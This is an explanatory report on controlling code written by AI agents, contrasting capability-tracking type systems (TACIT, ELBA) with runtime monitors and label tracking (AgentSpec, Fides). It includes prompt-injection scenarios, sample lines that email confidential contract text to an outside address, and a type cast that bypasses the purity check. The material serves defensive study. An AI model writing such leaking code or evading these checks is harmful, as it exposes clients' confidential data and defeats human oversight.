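# Static types versus runtime monitoring for controlling the code that AI agents write

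## What does it mean to enforce a rule on code that an AI agent writes?

Static type checking and runtime monitoring are two ways to enforce a policy, a rule that separates permitted from forbidden behaviour, on a program. A type checker, which is one form of static check, analyses the program's text and accepts or rejects it before any of it runs. A runtime monitor intercepts each action as the program attempts it and can allow, change or stop it. Both methods were developed for code that people wrote. They now have a new use because AI agents often act by writing a short program that runs at once, usually before anyone has read it.

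### Acting by writing code

An AI agent is a large language model that can use tools, such as functions that open files, query a database or send email. In the older arrangement, the model calls these tools one at a time. *Code Mode*, a 2025 post by Varda and Pai for the infrastructure company Cloudflare, explains that the model emits a special marker, then a short JSON message that names a tool and its arguments, then a closing marker. The surrounding software pauses the model, runs the tool and adds the result to the model's input. Even if the result is needed only for the next call, the model has to copy it out again. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) still describes this way of calling tools as the dominant interface in deployed systems.

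The alternative is to let the model write a script that calls several tools, stores their results in variables, and uses loops and conditions. *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2024) made an early case for this approach. In its design, each action is a piece of Python, and the model receives the output or error message as its next observation. On 82 tasks that typically needed several tools, the best model tested, a version of GPT-4, solved 74.4% when it acted through code and 53.7% when it acted through formatted text.

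Newer models gain less from writing scripts instead of JSON calls. Patel and colleagues compared the two on 14 models, and scripts did as well or better on 11. The other three, all from OpenAI, did worse with scripts because they wrote the characters that stand for a line break where a real line break belonged, so their longer scripts would not run.

Letting an agent write scripts that call tools is mainly useful for bulk work. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, a page of developer documentation, gives the example of checking 20 employees' expenses against their budgets. Separate calls take 20 round trips through the model and fill its input with thousands of expense lines, whereas one script does all the lookups and returns only the names of those who overspent. In Anthropic's own tests on an agent with 75 tools, scripts cut billed input tokens by roughly 38% without changing accuracy.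 On customer-service tasks with only one or two calls per turn, scripts raised the cost by about 8%.

Consider an assistant that summarises confidential contracts. A lawyer asks it to read a folder of them, save a summary where she can open it, and email her when the summary is ready. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, built their design around a similar case. The assistant might write this:

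```
texts   = read_all("contracts/")
summary = summarise(texts)
write("summaries/march.txt", summary)
send_email("lawyer@firm.example", "The summary is ready.")
```

The function `summarise` passes the contracts to a second model that the law firm runs on its own machines. The firm needs the second model because the one that writes the script belongs to an outside company with no right to see the contracts.

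### Why the script is untrusted

Even a well-meaning model makes mistakes. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) presents a system in which a model fills gaps in a program with code while the program runs. The paper treats an honest model as an unreliable programmer that may write incorrect code or try to access a resource it was not meant to have. The contracts assistant could accidentally read the parent folder and summarise the personnel files too.

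Prompt injection is a deliberate attack that uses text, often hidden in data an agent reads, to make the agent follow an attacker's instructions. For example, a counterparty could bury a sentence in a contract telling any AI system that reads it to forward the whole folder. Zhao and colleagues regard such text's influence on the model as unavoidable once the text is in the prompt, so they try to limit what an influenced model can do rather than prevent the influence.

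Odersky and colleagues go further and allow for a model that cooperates fully with the attacker. They take up the objection that this is too strict, since frontier models already resist many injections. Their reply is partly that some attacks still work: they cite the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who extracted user data through Anthropic's Files API. They also expect companies to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, and at that scale simple mistakes are likely to become serious vulnerabilities. I̶n̶ practice the strict assumption costs less than it seems to, because the same bad line can come from any of these causes:

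```
send_email("someone@elsewhere.example", texts[0])
```

An AI agent could write code that breaks a rule because of a mistake, a prompt injection or a hostile model, and a check on the code works the same way in every case.

Any guarantee still depends on some parts of the system working correctly, which together are called the trusted base. For Odersky and colleagues, it consists of the compiler, the library of tool functions, the runtime that executes accepted code, and the local model that handles confidential text. If `summarise` posted its input to a website, inspecting the assistant's four lines would not reveal it.

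### From request to observation

TACIT, the system that Odersky and colleagues built for the programming language Scala, gives a concrete path for such a script to follow.

1. Generation. The model writes the script and submits it as text. Nothing has happened yet outside the model.
2. Type check. The Scala compiler compares the script with the declared types of every function it uses. In TACIT those types also record capabilities, the unforgeable values that code must hold in order to write a file or open a connection. The static check sits here. If the compiler rejects the script, its error messages go back to the model, which tries again.
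3. Execution. The accepted script runs, and it can reach files, other processes and the network only through the trusted library. A monitor sits at those calls. A sandbox surrounds the whole step: it is a restricted environment that limits which files, network hosts and system functions the process can reach.
4. Observation. The script's output returns to the model, which uses it to decide what to do next.

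Commercial services can enforce rules at the same points, though the ones documented by OpenAI and Anthropic leave policy checks mainly to the sandbox and the customer's application. OpenAI's documentation page *Programmatic Tool Calling* describes a sandbox that gives each script a fresh, isolated JavaScript runtime with no direct network access, no general-purpose file system and no way to start other programs. When the script calls one of the customer's own tools, it pauses while the customer's application runs the tool and returns the result. A monitor can run during that pause, and OpenAI advises developers to check arguments and permissions at that point, on every call. It also recommends direct tool calls, outside any script, for writes and for actions that need approval.

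Printing the summary in the last step would disclose it to an outside company, because whatever the script prints goes into the input of a model that the company hosts. When a script prints confidential text, TACIT therefore shows the real words in the lawyer's terminal but sends the agent only the placeholder `Classified(****)`.

A static check on an agent's code happens before a snippet runs, but in the middle of the agent's task. A software company normally type-checks a program before shipping it. An agent writes its scripts as it works, so earlier scripts may have already read files or sent messages by the time a new one is checked. Zhao and colleagues compile each snippet against the program around it, with the variables and functions available at that point, as though a developer had typed it there.

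Their example of an account balance of 100 shows why it helps to type-check a whole snippet before running it. A model writes a snippet that subtracts 50 and then returns a sentence where the program expects a number. The compiler rejects the whole snippet, so the balance stays at 100. An interpreter that detects type errors only when it reaches them would already have subtracted the 50. But type checking doesn't undo the effects of a snippet that fails after the compiler accepts it. If the mail server fails during the fourth line of the contracts script, the summary file from the third line is still there.

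### Five requirements on the contracts assistant

A trace is the sequence of observable actions that a program performs in one run. The trace of the script above is some reads, one write and one send. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) defines a trace in nearly the same way, as the tool calls in a run that have an observable side effect, but this report also counts reads. Suppose the law firm sets five requirements.

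(A) The assistant reads only the contracts folder. This is an access requirement, which limits the resources the program may use. If the trace is a₁, a₂, …, aₙ, then every aᵢ that is a read must name a path inside the folder, so each action can be checked without looking at the others.

(B) Contract text never reaches an outside party. This is an information-flow requirement, a rule about where data, and anything computed from it, may go. Checking each action separately is not enough to enforce it. Odersky and colleagues point out that an agent can read a private file through one permitted call and then contact its cloud model through another. The data leaks by moving from the first call to the second, and that movement never crosses the sandbox boundary.

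A strict version of B is noninterference, the property that secret inputs make no difference to what an outsider can observe. If the script runs once on contracts *c* and once on different contracts *c′*, with everything else the same, the outsider must see the same thing both times. This rules out leaks that involve no copying, such as the assistant emailing an outsider "all fine" only when the contracts contain no penalty clause. The email quotes nothing, but the outsider can tell whether the contracts contain such a clause.

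(C) The assistant sends at most one email. This requirement is history-dependent, because whether an action is allowed depends on what the program has already done. A second email violates it even if it has the same recipient and wording as the first, because it comes later in the trace.

(D) The summary is accurate. This is a correctness requirement, which means the program's result must be what it is supposed to be. A script can read the right files, keep them secret, send one email and still report the wrong termination date. The list of actions would not reveal that error, so someone or something has to compare the summary with the contracts. Odersky and colleagues explicitly exclude correctness from what TACIT promises.

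(E) The assistant eventually delivers a summary. This is a liveness requirement, which means that something good must eventually happen, whereas A and C forbid particular events. However long the lawyer has waited, the summary could still arrive, so no unfinished trace proves that the assistant has broken the rule. Without E, an assistant that does nothing would meet A, B and C.

### The claim for types

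Odersky and colleagues give four reasons for enforcing such rules with a type system. Types catch errors before the agent's program runs, add no monitoring overhead, give guarantees that hold for all inputs, and are modular, so developers can build an agent's environment from reusable parts whose safety follows from their types. In the contracts assistant, a script that mails `texts[0]` to a stranger would never start, a script that passes the type check would need no monitoring and would stay safe whatever the contracts contain, and the firm could reuse a safe `summarise` function in another assistant.

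Zhou and colleagues supply a precise form of the third reason. Let traces(*e*) be the set of all traces that a program *e* can produce. A type *t* guarantees a property *P* if

*e* has type *t* ⟹ *P*(traces(*e*)) holds, for every program *e* in the language.

The checker's guarantee covers every possible run, including runs on contracts that nobody has drafted yet. It holds only if the checker is sound, meaning that all the code it accepts obeys the policy.

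The claim is narrower than it may sound. "No monitoring overhead" can apply only to what the types guarantee, and TACIT leaves some checks to run time. For instance, its library checks file paths while the script runs and refuses any outside the folder the script asked for, so requirement A already rests partly on a runtime check. The original wording also contrasts all inputs with "only the tested ones", which is an argument against relying on testing. A monitor checks every run that takes place, whatever the input, so the advantage of types over monitoring must come from something other than better coverage of test inputs.

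## How can a type checker keep generated code within its permissions?

An ordinary type checker would accept the line that emails a contract to a stranger, because `send_email` expects two strings, and the stranger's address and `texts[0]` are both strings. To reject that line, a checker needs types that also record information such as what a piece of code can do to the outside world or where a value came from. In TACIT, which uses Scala, a value's type lists the capabilities that the value can use. ELBA, which Zhou and colleagues built in Haskell, gives the whole script a type that fixes which effects the script may have.

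### Capture sets in TACIT

Scala has an extension called capture checking, which adds to a type the list of capabilities, such as file handles, that a value of that type may hold and use. This list is the capture set. Suppose a script holds `fs`, a capability for part of the file system, and contains these lines:

```
val f     = fs.access("summaries/march.txt")
val save  = (s: String) => f.write(s)
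val clean = (s: String) => s.trim
```

The function `save` takes a string and writes it to a file. Its type is `String ->{f} Unit`, where `Unit` means that it returns no useful value and `{f}` is the capture set. The compiler puts `f` there because the function's body writes through `f`. The function `clean` only strips spaces, so its capture set is empty and its type is `String -> String`. A function with an empty capture set is pure, so it can compute a result from its input but can't write a file, send a message or have any other side effect.

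The compiler infers these sets from the code, so scripts rarely need to write them out. A capability hidden inside another object still appears in the types. In an example from Odersky and colleagues, a logger that writes to a file called `out` has the type `Logger^{out}`. The compiler treats the logger itself as a capability, and any function that calls it has the logger in its own capture set.

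If a library function takes an argument of type `A ->{D} B` and the script passes a function of type `A ->{C} B`, the compiler accepts it when C ⊆ D. The type `A -> B` means D is empty, so only a pure function fits, while `A => B` puts no limit on D.

A capture set lists everything a function might use, even if a particular run doesn't use all of it. A function that writes to `f` only on Sundays has the same type as one that writes to it every time. The compiler therefore rejects some harmless code, but it never has to predict which branch will run.

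Odersky and colleagues point out that earlier capability languages, such as E, relied on run-time mechanisms alone. A library then can't distinguish a function with a mailer hidden inside it from a harmless one, so it can't use types to require a pure function. TACIT's protection of confidential text depends on this requirement.

### Requirement A: file access that ends with its block

Requirement A says that the assistant may read only the contracts folder. TACIT gives out file access through a function called `requestFileSystem`, which takes a folder and a block of code. It creates a file-system capability for the folder, passes it to the block, and invalidates it when the block returns. The compiler accepts this script (TACIT's own library passes `fs` implicitly, so real scripts are a little shorter):

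```
val text = requestFileSystem("contracts") { fs =>
  fs.access("contracts/acme.txt").readClassified()
}
```

The block returns the text of one contract inside a wrapper of type `Classified[String]`, which holds data but no capability. Now suppose the script tries to keep its file access by returning a function that reads files:

```
val reader = requestFileSystem("contracts") { fs =>
  (name: String) => fs.access(name).readClassified()
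}
```

The compiler infers that this block returns a value of type `String ->{fs} Classified[String]`. But `requestFileSystem` must return a value whose type is valid outside the block, where `fs` doesn't exist. No capture set there can include `fs`, so the types don't match and the compiler rejects the script. Zhao and colleagues print the error for a nearly identical snippet with a capability named `io`. The compiler found `String ->{io} String` where it required a function type whose capture set belongs to the code outside the block, and it reported that `io` "outlives its scope".

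This matters most in a session with many turns. The file access the script needed for the lawyer's first request is no longer available by her second, but the wrapped text is still available for follow-up questions.

The rule limits how long the assistant has access, but not which folder it gets. The folder's name is just a string, so a script that opens `"personnel"` has the same type as one that opens `"contracts"`. The types guarantee only that every read goes through a file-system capability, and someone has to decide what that capability covers. In a scenario from Odersky and colleagues, the developer does this before the agent starts by writing a small environment object that contains one output file and a document database covering only the contracts folder. If the script has no other source of files, it has no way to refer to the personnel records.

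### Requirement B: text that only pure functions can touch

Requirement B says that contract text must never reach an outside party. The `Classified` wrapper enforces it mainly through one method:

```
def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The method applies a function `f` to the hidden content and wraps the result again. Because the arrow in the type of `f` has an empty capture set, `f` must be pure. The compiler accepts the following lines, in which `chat` sends wrapped text to the law firm's own model and returns a wrapped answer:

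```
val request = text.map(t => "Summarise this contract: " + t)
val summary = chat(request)
```

Suppose the firm has also added a capability named `mail` to the library. The stranger's email then looks like this:

```
text.map(t => mail.send("someone@elsewhere.example", t))
```

The compiler rejects the script because `map` requires a function of type `String -> Unit`, but the script passes one of type `String ->{mail} Unit`, and `{mail}` is not a subset of the empty set. Odersky and colleagues collected errors of this form from programs in their benchmarks. In one, a script tried to write classified security recommendations to a file from inside `map`, and the compiler reported that the file's capability could not flow into an empty capture set.

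The script could also try to pass `text` directly to `mail.send`, without using `map`. The type checker rejects this because `mail.send` expects a `String` and `text` is a `Classified[String]`. TACIT needs both restrictions. If the wrapper accepted impure functions, the script could send the text from inside it, and if `mail.send` accepted wrapped values, the script could send the text directly even though `map` requires pure functions.

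The assistant could also leak a fact about the contracts without copying any text, for example by emailing "all fine" only if there is no penalty clause. The same types prevent this. A script can test for the clause with `text.map(t => t.contains("penalty"))`, but the result is a `Classified[Boolean]`. An `if` statement needs a plain `Boolean`, so the script can't use the result outside `map` to decide whether to send an email. Inside `map`, it can branch on the answer but can't send anything. The length of a contract is also wrapped in `Classified`.

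The rule is stricter than requirement B. Emailing the summary to the lawyer herself would be fine, but the compiler rejects that too because `mail.send` takes only plain strings. Any legitimate release of wrapped content has to go through a function that the firm puts into its trusted library. In Odersky and colleagues' design, `Classified` has a `reveal` method that gives the plain content to any code holding a `CanAccess` capability, which the agent never receives. For some of their tests, they also wrote a `displaySecurely` function, which shows wrapped text to the user without passing it through the agent's model. The compiler can't check whether such a function discloses too much.

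Purity also makes the script less flexible. The hosted model writes the function for `map` without access to the contract, so it cannot adapt the analysis to its contents. Zhao and colleagues address this by letting the function call a trusted local model, which reads the contract and writes further code to suit it. Before the new code runs, the compiler checks it under the same ban on capabilities.

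### Effect types and hidden constructors in ELBA

Haskell functions are pure by default, so ELBA can recognise a harmless function without capture sets. A computation that reads files, uses the network or otherwise interacts with the outside world has a type that starts with `IO`, such as `IO String`. Any computation that includes an `IO` operation as a step also has an `IO` type.

Zhou and colleagues illustrate the consequence with a calculator. A developer asks a model for a program whose result must be an `Int`, a whole number. A malicious user types a request to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. If the model writes that program, its type is `IO Int`, which doesn't match `Int`, so the compiler rejects it. The developer needs no rule against deleting files, because a program of type `Int` can only calculate.

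Most agents do need some effects. ELBA's answer is a custom effect type, which permits a few chosen operations and no others. In the main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry it writes has to come from DBLP, an online database of computer science papers. The developer supplies three functions, whose types are, in outline:

```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
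appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a paper's permanent identifier, and `()` means a function returns no useful value. The developer also sets the expected type of the agent's whole script to `BibIO ()`. The agent can then combine the three functions with any pure code. For example, it can search for a topic, fetch all the entries, sort them by year and save the earliest.

`BibIO` and `Trusted` together restrict which operations the script can perform and what data it can use in them. Suppose the model makes up an entry. Haskell's standard function `writeFile` could put the text straight into the bibliography, but a call to it has the type `IO ()`, and the compiler requires `BibIO ()`. The script could call `appendToBibFile` instead, but the invented entry is a `String` and the function requires a `Trusted Bib`. The script cannot convert the string, because the developer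 keeps the constructor of `Trusted` (the function that builds its values) private to the library. The only way to get a `Trusted Bib` is to fetch one from DBLP.

The type `Trusted Bib` records where an entry came from, not whether it is correct or relevant. An error in DBLP would go into the bibliography unchanged. Zhou and colleagues ran 100 tasks in which an agent had to write a list of citations on a computer science topic, and they counted a citation as hallucinated if its authors, year or DOI were wrong. None of ELBA's 925 citations were hallucinated, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from an untyped agent with the same model and a web search tool. This result is consistent with the guarantee, but it doesn't show how much of the difference is due to types. The untyped agent wrote its citations from search results and memory, so giving it a function that copies whole records from DBLP might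 have removed most of the errors.

ELBA handles requirement A with another hidden constructor. A script reads a file with `readRIO`, which takes a `Path` rather than a string, so a script that calls `readRIO "personnel/salaries.txt"` doesn't compile. The application gives the script a `Path` for the contracts folder, and the script can narrow it to a file inside. The library checks at run time whether a narrowed path stays inside the folder. In ELBA, the application chooses the folder, whereas with TACIT's `requestFileSystem` the script names it. For requirement B, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that attaches labels to data and compares them at run time.

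TACIT also covers less of the application than ELBA does. It is a server that an existing agent can connect to as a tool, and its compiler checks only the scripts that the agent submits. An ELBA developer writes the whole application in Haskell, including the code that calls the model. A company with a working agent in Python would have to rewrite it to use ELBA, but the same typed rules would then apply to both the surrounding program and the generated script.

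### Closing the ways around the types

The arguments so far rely on types accurately describing what the code can do. Odersky and colleagues set out three conditions for this, each of which rules out a different way for code to do something its type doesn't show.

*Capability safety* means that code can't forge a capability or drop the requirement to have one. If a script could construct its own `CanAccess` value, it could call `reveal` and read every contract.

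*Capability completeness* means that capabilities govern every effect that matters for safety, except those that the system confines at run time. Suppose a script could call a standard Java function that writes files without requiring a capability. The compiler would add nothing to the capture set, and a function that copied contracts to a shared disk would count as pure. Each new tool can create another such gap. The abstract of a conference talk, Scala Days' *AI on your desktop* (2026), warns that an assistant with a web browser could open local files in it, or take a screenshot of a sensitive application and send the image to a cloud service. The talk proposes a separate browser capability and classified versions of pages and images.

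*Local purity* means that the type system can require a chosen piece of code to use only certain capabilities, or none, while the rest of the script can still have side effects. The `map` method depends on local purity.

Full Scala doesn't meet these conditions, because it has features that let a programmer overrule the type checker. A type cast is the simplest example. It instructs the compiler to treat a value as having a different type:

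```
val leak = (t: String) => mail.send("someone@elsewhere.example", t)
text.map(leak.asInstanceOf[String -> Unit])
```

The function `leak` has the type `String ->{mail} Unit`. The cast relabels it as `String -> Unit`, which is what `map` requires, so the comparison succeeds and the email goes out. Programmers sometimes have good reasons to use casts, but a hostile script can bypass the permission check with a single cast.

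Scala's designers added safe mode, a restricted version of the language for code that nobody has reviewed. According to Scala's official *Safe Mode* reference, it forbids unchecked casts, unchecked pattern matches, `@unchecked` annotations and the `caps.unsafe` library module, since all of these can stop the compiler from tracking a capability. It also forbids reflection, which lets a program look up functions by name while it runs, because the compiler can't add a capability to a capture set if it can't detect the call that uses that capability.

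Safe mode also tracks changes to variables. Without that, a script could define an empty variable outside `map`, copy the contract into it inside `map`, and email the variable afterwards. The text would be out of its wrapper before any step involved a file or a network connection.

Finally, a script in safe mode can use global functions and objects only if they were also written in safe mode or are marked `@assumeSafe`. The annotation is for library code that a person has reviewed but the compiler can't approve. One example from Scala is a mailer that shows each message to the user and sends it only after the user agrees. The script can't call the underlying mail function directly. The compiler accepts the annotation without checking it, so if the reviewer misses a security hole, later checks of the script won't find it. Scripts can't use the annotation themselves because an agent could then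 approve its own code, as the software company VirtusLab explains in a walk-through of safe mode.

Safe mode leaves one known gap in the static check. A function inside `map` could throw an exception with contract text in its error message. Almost any code can fail, such as by dividing by zero or running out of memory, so tracking every exception in Scala's types is considered impractical. The system that runs the script therefore has to catch exceptions and turn them into ordinary values, which TACIT can then wrap like other confidential data.

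Haskell's equivalent of the cast is `unsafePerformIO`, a function that takes a computation of type `IO Int` and returns a plain `Int`, although the computation can still read or delete data. If the calculator's malicious program used this function, it would have the expected type. Zhou and colleagues point to Safe Haskell, a restricted version of the language from 2012 that excludes such features. Developers can select it with a compiler setting. The two restricted languages have the same purpose, but people have had much longer to find faults in Safe Haskell.

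Scala's safe mode, a subset of the language that developers turn on by importing `language.experimental.safe`, is still experimental. Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* introduced it, and the notes for the next release candidate, *github scala/scala3 3.8.4-RC1*, list fixes to its checks. Safe mode did not become stable in Scala 3.9, the long-term release of September 2026. Mazur's *Scala 3.9 LTS released!* lists neither safe mode nor capture checking among the three features due to move to the preview stage in version 3.10. That version came out in October, and the summary in Scala Times' *Issue 630* (2026) mentions no change to either. The official introduction to capture checking, Scala's *Capture Checking Basics*, calls it "still highly experimental and unstable".

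That label matters for security because the compiler is part of the trusted base. Researchers have machine-checked proofs that the basic type system behind capture checking is sound. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that they still need a proof that safe mode ensures capability safety and local purity. Even with both proofs, the compiler could contain a bug that the mathematical model does not. A law firm that adopted TACIT today would be relying on a young implementation of a good design, which is a reason to keep a sandbox around it.

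### What happens after a rejection

The model starts with a prompt, then corrects any code that is rejected. In LACUNA, the related system by Zhao and colleagues, the prompt contains the task, the expected type, the surrounding source code with a gap for the new code, and a list of the variables available there. The expected type restricts what the model can write and also helps it interpret the task. Zhou and colleagues give the example of the prompt "parse this". If the surrounding program then sorts the results by year, Haskell can infer that each result must be a date, and ELBA passes that information to the model.

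When generated code fails to compile, LACUNA resends the original prompt with the compiler's errors appended. Its simplified code allows three attempts by default. If all of them fail, the program receives an exception containing the last errors, and the developer can decide what to do next. ELBA works in much the same way. Under its standing instructions, the model should respond to a follow-up message containing a compiler error with one corrected expression of the same type. TACIT has no separate retry mechanism. It returns the error as the output of the tool call, and the agent decides whether to try again, as it would after any other failed call.

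A capture-checking error shows the type that the compiler found, the type that it required, and the capability that caused the mismatch. A model that tried by mistake to save a classified summary with the ordinary `write` function can use the error to identify the file handle as the problem and switch to `writeClassified`. Many rejections have nothing to do with security. In tests on customer-service tasks, Odersky and colleagues often saw scripts fail because the model had not handled a value that could be missing, or had typed a dollar sign where Scala reads it as the start of a variable name.

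The error messages are safe to show to the outside company's model. The compiler produces them from the source code and the types, before the script opens any contracts, so they can't contain contract text.

A hostile model can use the loop too. It learns from each error which rule stopped it, and it can try something else. Retrying won't get forbidden code past a sound checker, but if the checker has a bug, the loop makes that bug easier to find. A limit on retries helps only a little, since the agent may be able to start a new task and continue the search.

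An honest model can also go wrong by writing code that satisfies the compiler without doing the job. In the bibliography example, the one-line script `return ()` does nothing, but it has the type `BibIO ()`, as a correct script would. A model may well write something like it after the compiler has rejected several attempts.

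## How does a runtime monitor decide whether an action may go ahead?

A runtime monitor checks an action when the script attempts it, when the actual file name, recipient and text are available. A compiler has to accept or reject the script before it runs, without knowing which files the script will find or what they contain.

### The reference monitor

Many agent monitors follow a design from the early 1970s called the reference monitor. The US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and it had to assume that one of them might write a hostile program. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, Anderson (1972) proposed checking every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do.

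The list can be a table with a row for each program, a column for each file or device, and the permitted operations in the cells. In the contracts assistant's row, the cell for the contracts folder would contain "read", the cell for the summaries folder would contain "write", and the cell for the personnel folder would be empty. These entries are enough for requirement A, that the assistant reads only the contracts folder.

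Anderson set three conditions for any mechanism that does this job:

- It must be tamper-proof, because a program that can alter the monitor can get past it.
- It must run on every attempt. If some program is exempt from the check, that program becomes part of the security machinery and has to meet the other two conditions itself.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly in all cases.

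Anderson used these conditions to explain why GCOS III, an operating system of the time, was insecure. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but this check was off while the operating system worked on the user's behalf. The operating system therefore had to count as part of the monitor, and at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions it was far too big to verify.

A line in a model's prompt, such as "never email a contract", meets none of the conditions. Injected text can override it, the model can fail to apply it, and nobody can test the model on every possible input.

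### A state machine for requirement C

A fixed table of permissions can't express requirement C, that the assistant sends at most one email, because the monitor has to keep a record of past actions. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) describes such monitors as security automata. A security automaton has a set of states, a starting state and a transition function, which gives the next state for each action permitted in the current state. The monitor blocks any action for which the function has no entry in that state.

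Two states are enough for requirement C:

```
                 send_email
  NONE SENT  ----------------->  ONE SENT

  any other action:              any other action:
  stay in NONE SENT              stay in ONE SENT

                                 send_email:
                                 no transition, so block
```

Suppose the assistant saves the summary and emails the lawyer, and then a faulty loop makes it email her again:

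| Attempted action | State before | Verdict | State after |
|---|---|---|---|
| `write("summaries/march.txt", summary)` | NONE SENT | allow | NONE SENT |
| `send_email("lawyer@firm.example", …)` | NONE SENT | allow | ONE SENT |
| `send_email("lawyer@firm.example", …)` | ONE SENT | block | ONE SENT |

*Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) divides the handling of each tool call into three steps: intercept, evaluate and commit. The monitor pauses the call and works out what state it would lead to. If the policy forbids that state, the monitor discards the state, blocks the call and sends the agent feedback so that it can try something else. Otherwise, the tool runs and the new state becomes the current one.

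Schneider's design works only if the monitor can stop the script and the script can't write to the variable that holds the state. The monitor also has to receive every event that counts as sending an email, whichever function the script uses. With an agent, the state also has to persist from one script to the next. If the assistant wrote five scripts in one session and the count restarted with each, it could send five emails.

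### Halting, suppressing and inserting

Schneider's automata end the program when it attempts something forbidden. *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) compares monitors of this kind with monitors that can edit the sequence of actions. An editing monitor can suppress an action and let the program continue, or insert an action the program never attempted.

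If the script attempts the extra email before saving its second summary, a monitor that can only halt the script would prevent that summary from being saved. A monitor that can suppress actions would block the email and let the script save the summary. One that can insert actions could also add an entry to an audit log.

An editing monitor can also hold back an action until later actions show whether it complies with the policy. Suppose the firm requires an entry in its client register for every saved summary. When the script tries to save a summary, the monitor reports success but withholds the write. If the script then makes the register entry, the monitor releases both actions together. If the script never makes the entry, the summary is never saved and the policy isn't violated. A monitor that can only halt the script must allow or block the write before it can determine whether the entry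 will follow, so it risks either permitting a violation or stopping a compliant script. Monitors that can edit actions can therefore enforce more policies than those that can only halt.

The method works only for actions that the monitor can convincingly fake. Ligatti and colleagues give email as a counterexample. If the script needs the reply before it can continue, the monitor has to send the message for real and can't take it back.

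Ligatti and colleagues also give two standards for a good monitor. A monitor is sound if the actions it lets through always obey the policy, and transparent if it preserves the meaning of every run that already obeyed the policy. A monitor that blocks everything can be sound, but it isn't transparent.

### AgentSpec: a trigger, a condition and a response

AgentSpec is a small language for writing rules about agents. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AGENTSPEC*, give each rule a trigger, which is an event that activates it, a list of conditions to check, and a response for when all the conditions are true. The law firm could write these two rules:

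```
rule @one_email
trigger SendEmail
check   email_already_sent
enforce stop
end

rule @known_recipient
trigger SendEmail
check   !is_firm_address
enforce user_inspection
end
```

Each condition is a Python function that returns true or false. It can use the user's request and the history of the run, so `email_already_sent` can check for an earlier email. By contrast, *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) finds that the defences shipped with agents mostly apply rules to individual calls, which isn't enough to enforce a policy about several steps.

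AgentSpec has four built-in responses. `stop` ends the task, and `user_inspection` asks the user whether to go ahead. `invoke_action` carries out an action that the rule's author chose in advance. `llm_self_examine` tells the model that it is about to break a rule and has it plan a different action.

The implementation plugs into LangChain, a common framework for building agents, at three points: before an action, after the action returns a result, and when the agent declares the task finished. A rule at the third point could help enforce requirement E, that a summary eventually arrives, by checking that the summary file exists and making the model continue if it doesn't.

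For agents that write code, the event that triggers an AgentSpec rule is the call to the Python interpreter, so a whole script counts as one action. The rule's conditions examine the script's source text. In one example, a script needs the user's approval if it both fetches a page from a website that isn't on an approved list and prints the content. This is a static check, and much rougher than type checking. Wang and colleagues accept that analyzing how data moves through the script would be more accurate. To monitor the separate actions inside a script, the firm would have to attach rules to the tool functions that the script calls.

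Commercial products use similar rules. According to *guardscope* (2026), Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit uses rules to decide on every tool call, and companies write such policies in specialised languages such as Rego and Cedar. The conditions can also be simple. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) uses small Python functions that check a call's arguments and the current contents of a database.

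### Fides and CaMeL: a label on every value

Requirement B, that contract text never reaches an outside party, is harder to express as a rule about calls. Schneider's main example of an automaton forbids sending any message after reading a file. That rule would keep the contracts secret, but it would also stop the assistant from telling the lawyer that her summary is ready. A more precise monitor needs a record of which data came from the contracts. Label tracking provides one by attaching a label to each value and working out a new label for everything computed from it.

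Fides is a label-tracking system from Microsoft. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe labels that list the people who may read a piece of data. Suppose the firm lets each company read its own contract. The label on the Acme contract is {lawyer, partner, Acme}, and the label on the Birch contract is {lawyer, partner, Birch}. A summary of both may go only to people on both lists:

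{lawyer, partner, Acme} ∩ {lawyer, partner, Birch} = {lawyer, partner}

Before a tool sends text anywhere, Fides checks that every recipient is on the text's list:

| Attempted email | Recipient | Permitted readers | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| the summary, to the lawyer | lawyer | lawyer, partner | allow |
| the summary, to Acme | Acme | lawyer, partner | block |
| the Acme contract, to a stranger | stranger | lawyer, partner, Acme | block |

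TACIT's compiler would reject all three. The monitor can allow the first because it has the recipient's address when it decides.

The company that hosts the assistant's model is also an outside party. Fides normally checks only tool calls, since Costa and colleagues assume that an attacker can't observe the model's input. The law firm can't rely on that assumption, but Costa and colleagues note that the check can run earlier, on everything the agent is about to do, which would include requests to the model.

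Fides gives data a second label, trusted or untrusted, to guard against prompt injection. Anything computed partly from untrusted data is untrusted, and a policy can require that consequential actions, such as sending an email, depend only on trusted data. A model's answer gets the combined label of everything in its input, because no one can tell precisely which parts influenced the answer. If the untrusted contracts entered the conversation, every later tool call would be untrusted, and this policy would stop the assistant from sending the lawyer her notice.

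Fides avoids this by hiding the contracts from the model that plans the task:

1. The tool returns the contract text, which would make the conversation untrusted. Fides stores the text in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name.
2. The model asks a second, isolated model to summarise the variable. The isolated model has no tools, and its answer goes into another variable with the same labels.
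3. The model asks to save the second variable in `summaries/march.txt`. Fides fills in the text and checks the call. The policy can insist on a trusted file name while accepting untrusted content.
4. The conversation is still trusted, so the assistant can email the lawyer that the summary is ready.

Some tasks require the planning model to learn something about the hidden text. Fides can restrict the isolated model's answer to a fixed form, such as yes or no, and record that form in the label. A policy could then allow further actions based on a yes-or-no answer drawn from a contract, but not on free text, because one bit can't contain an attacker's instructions.

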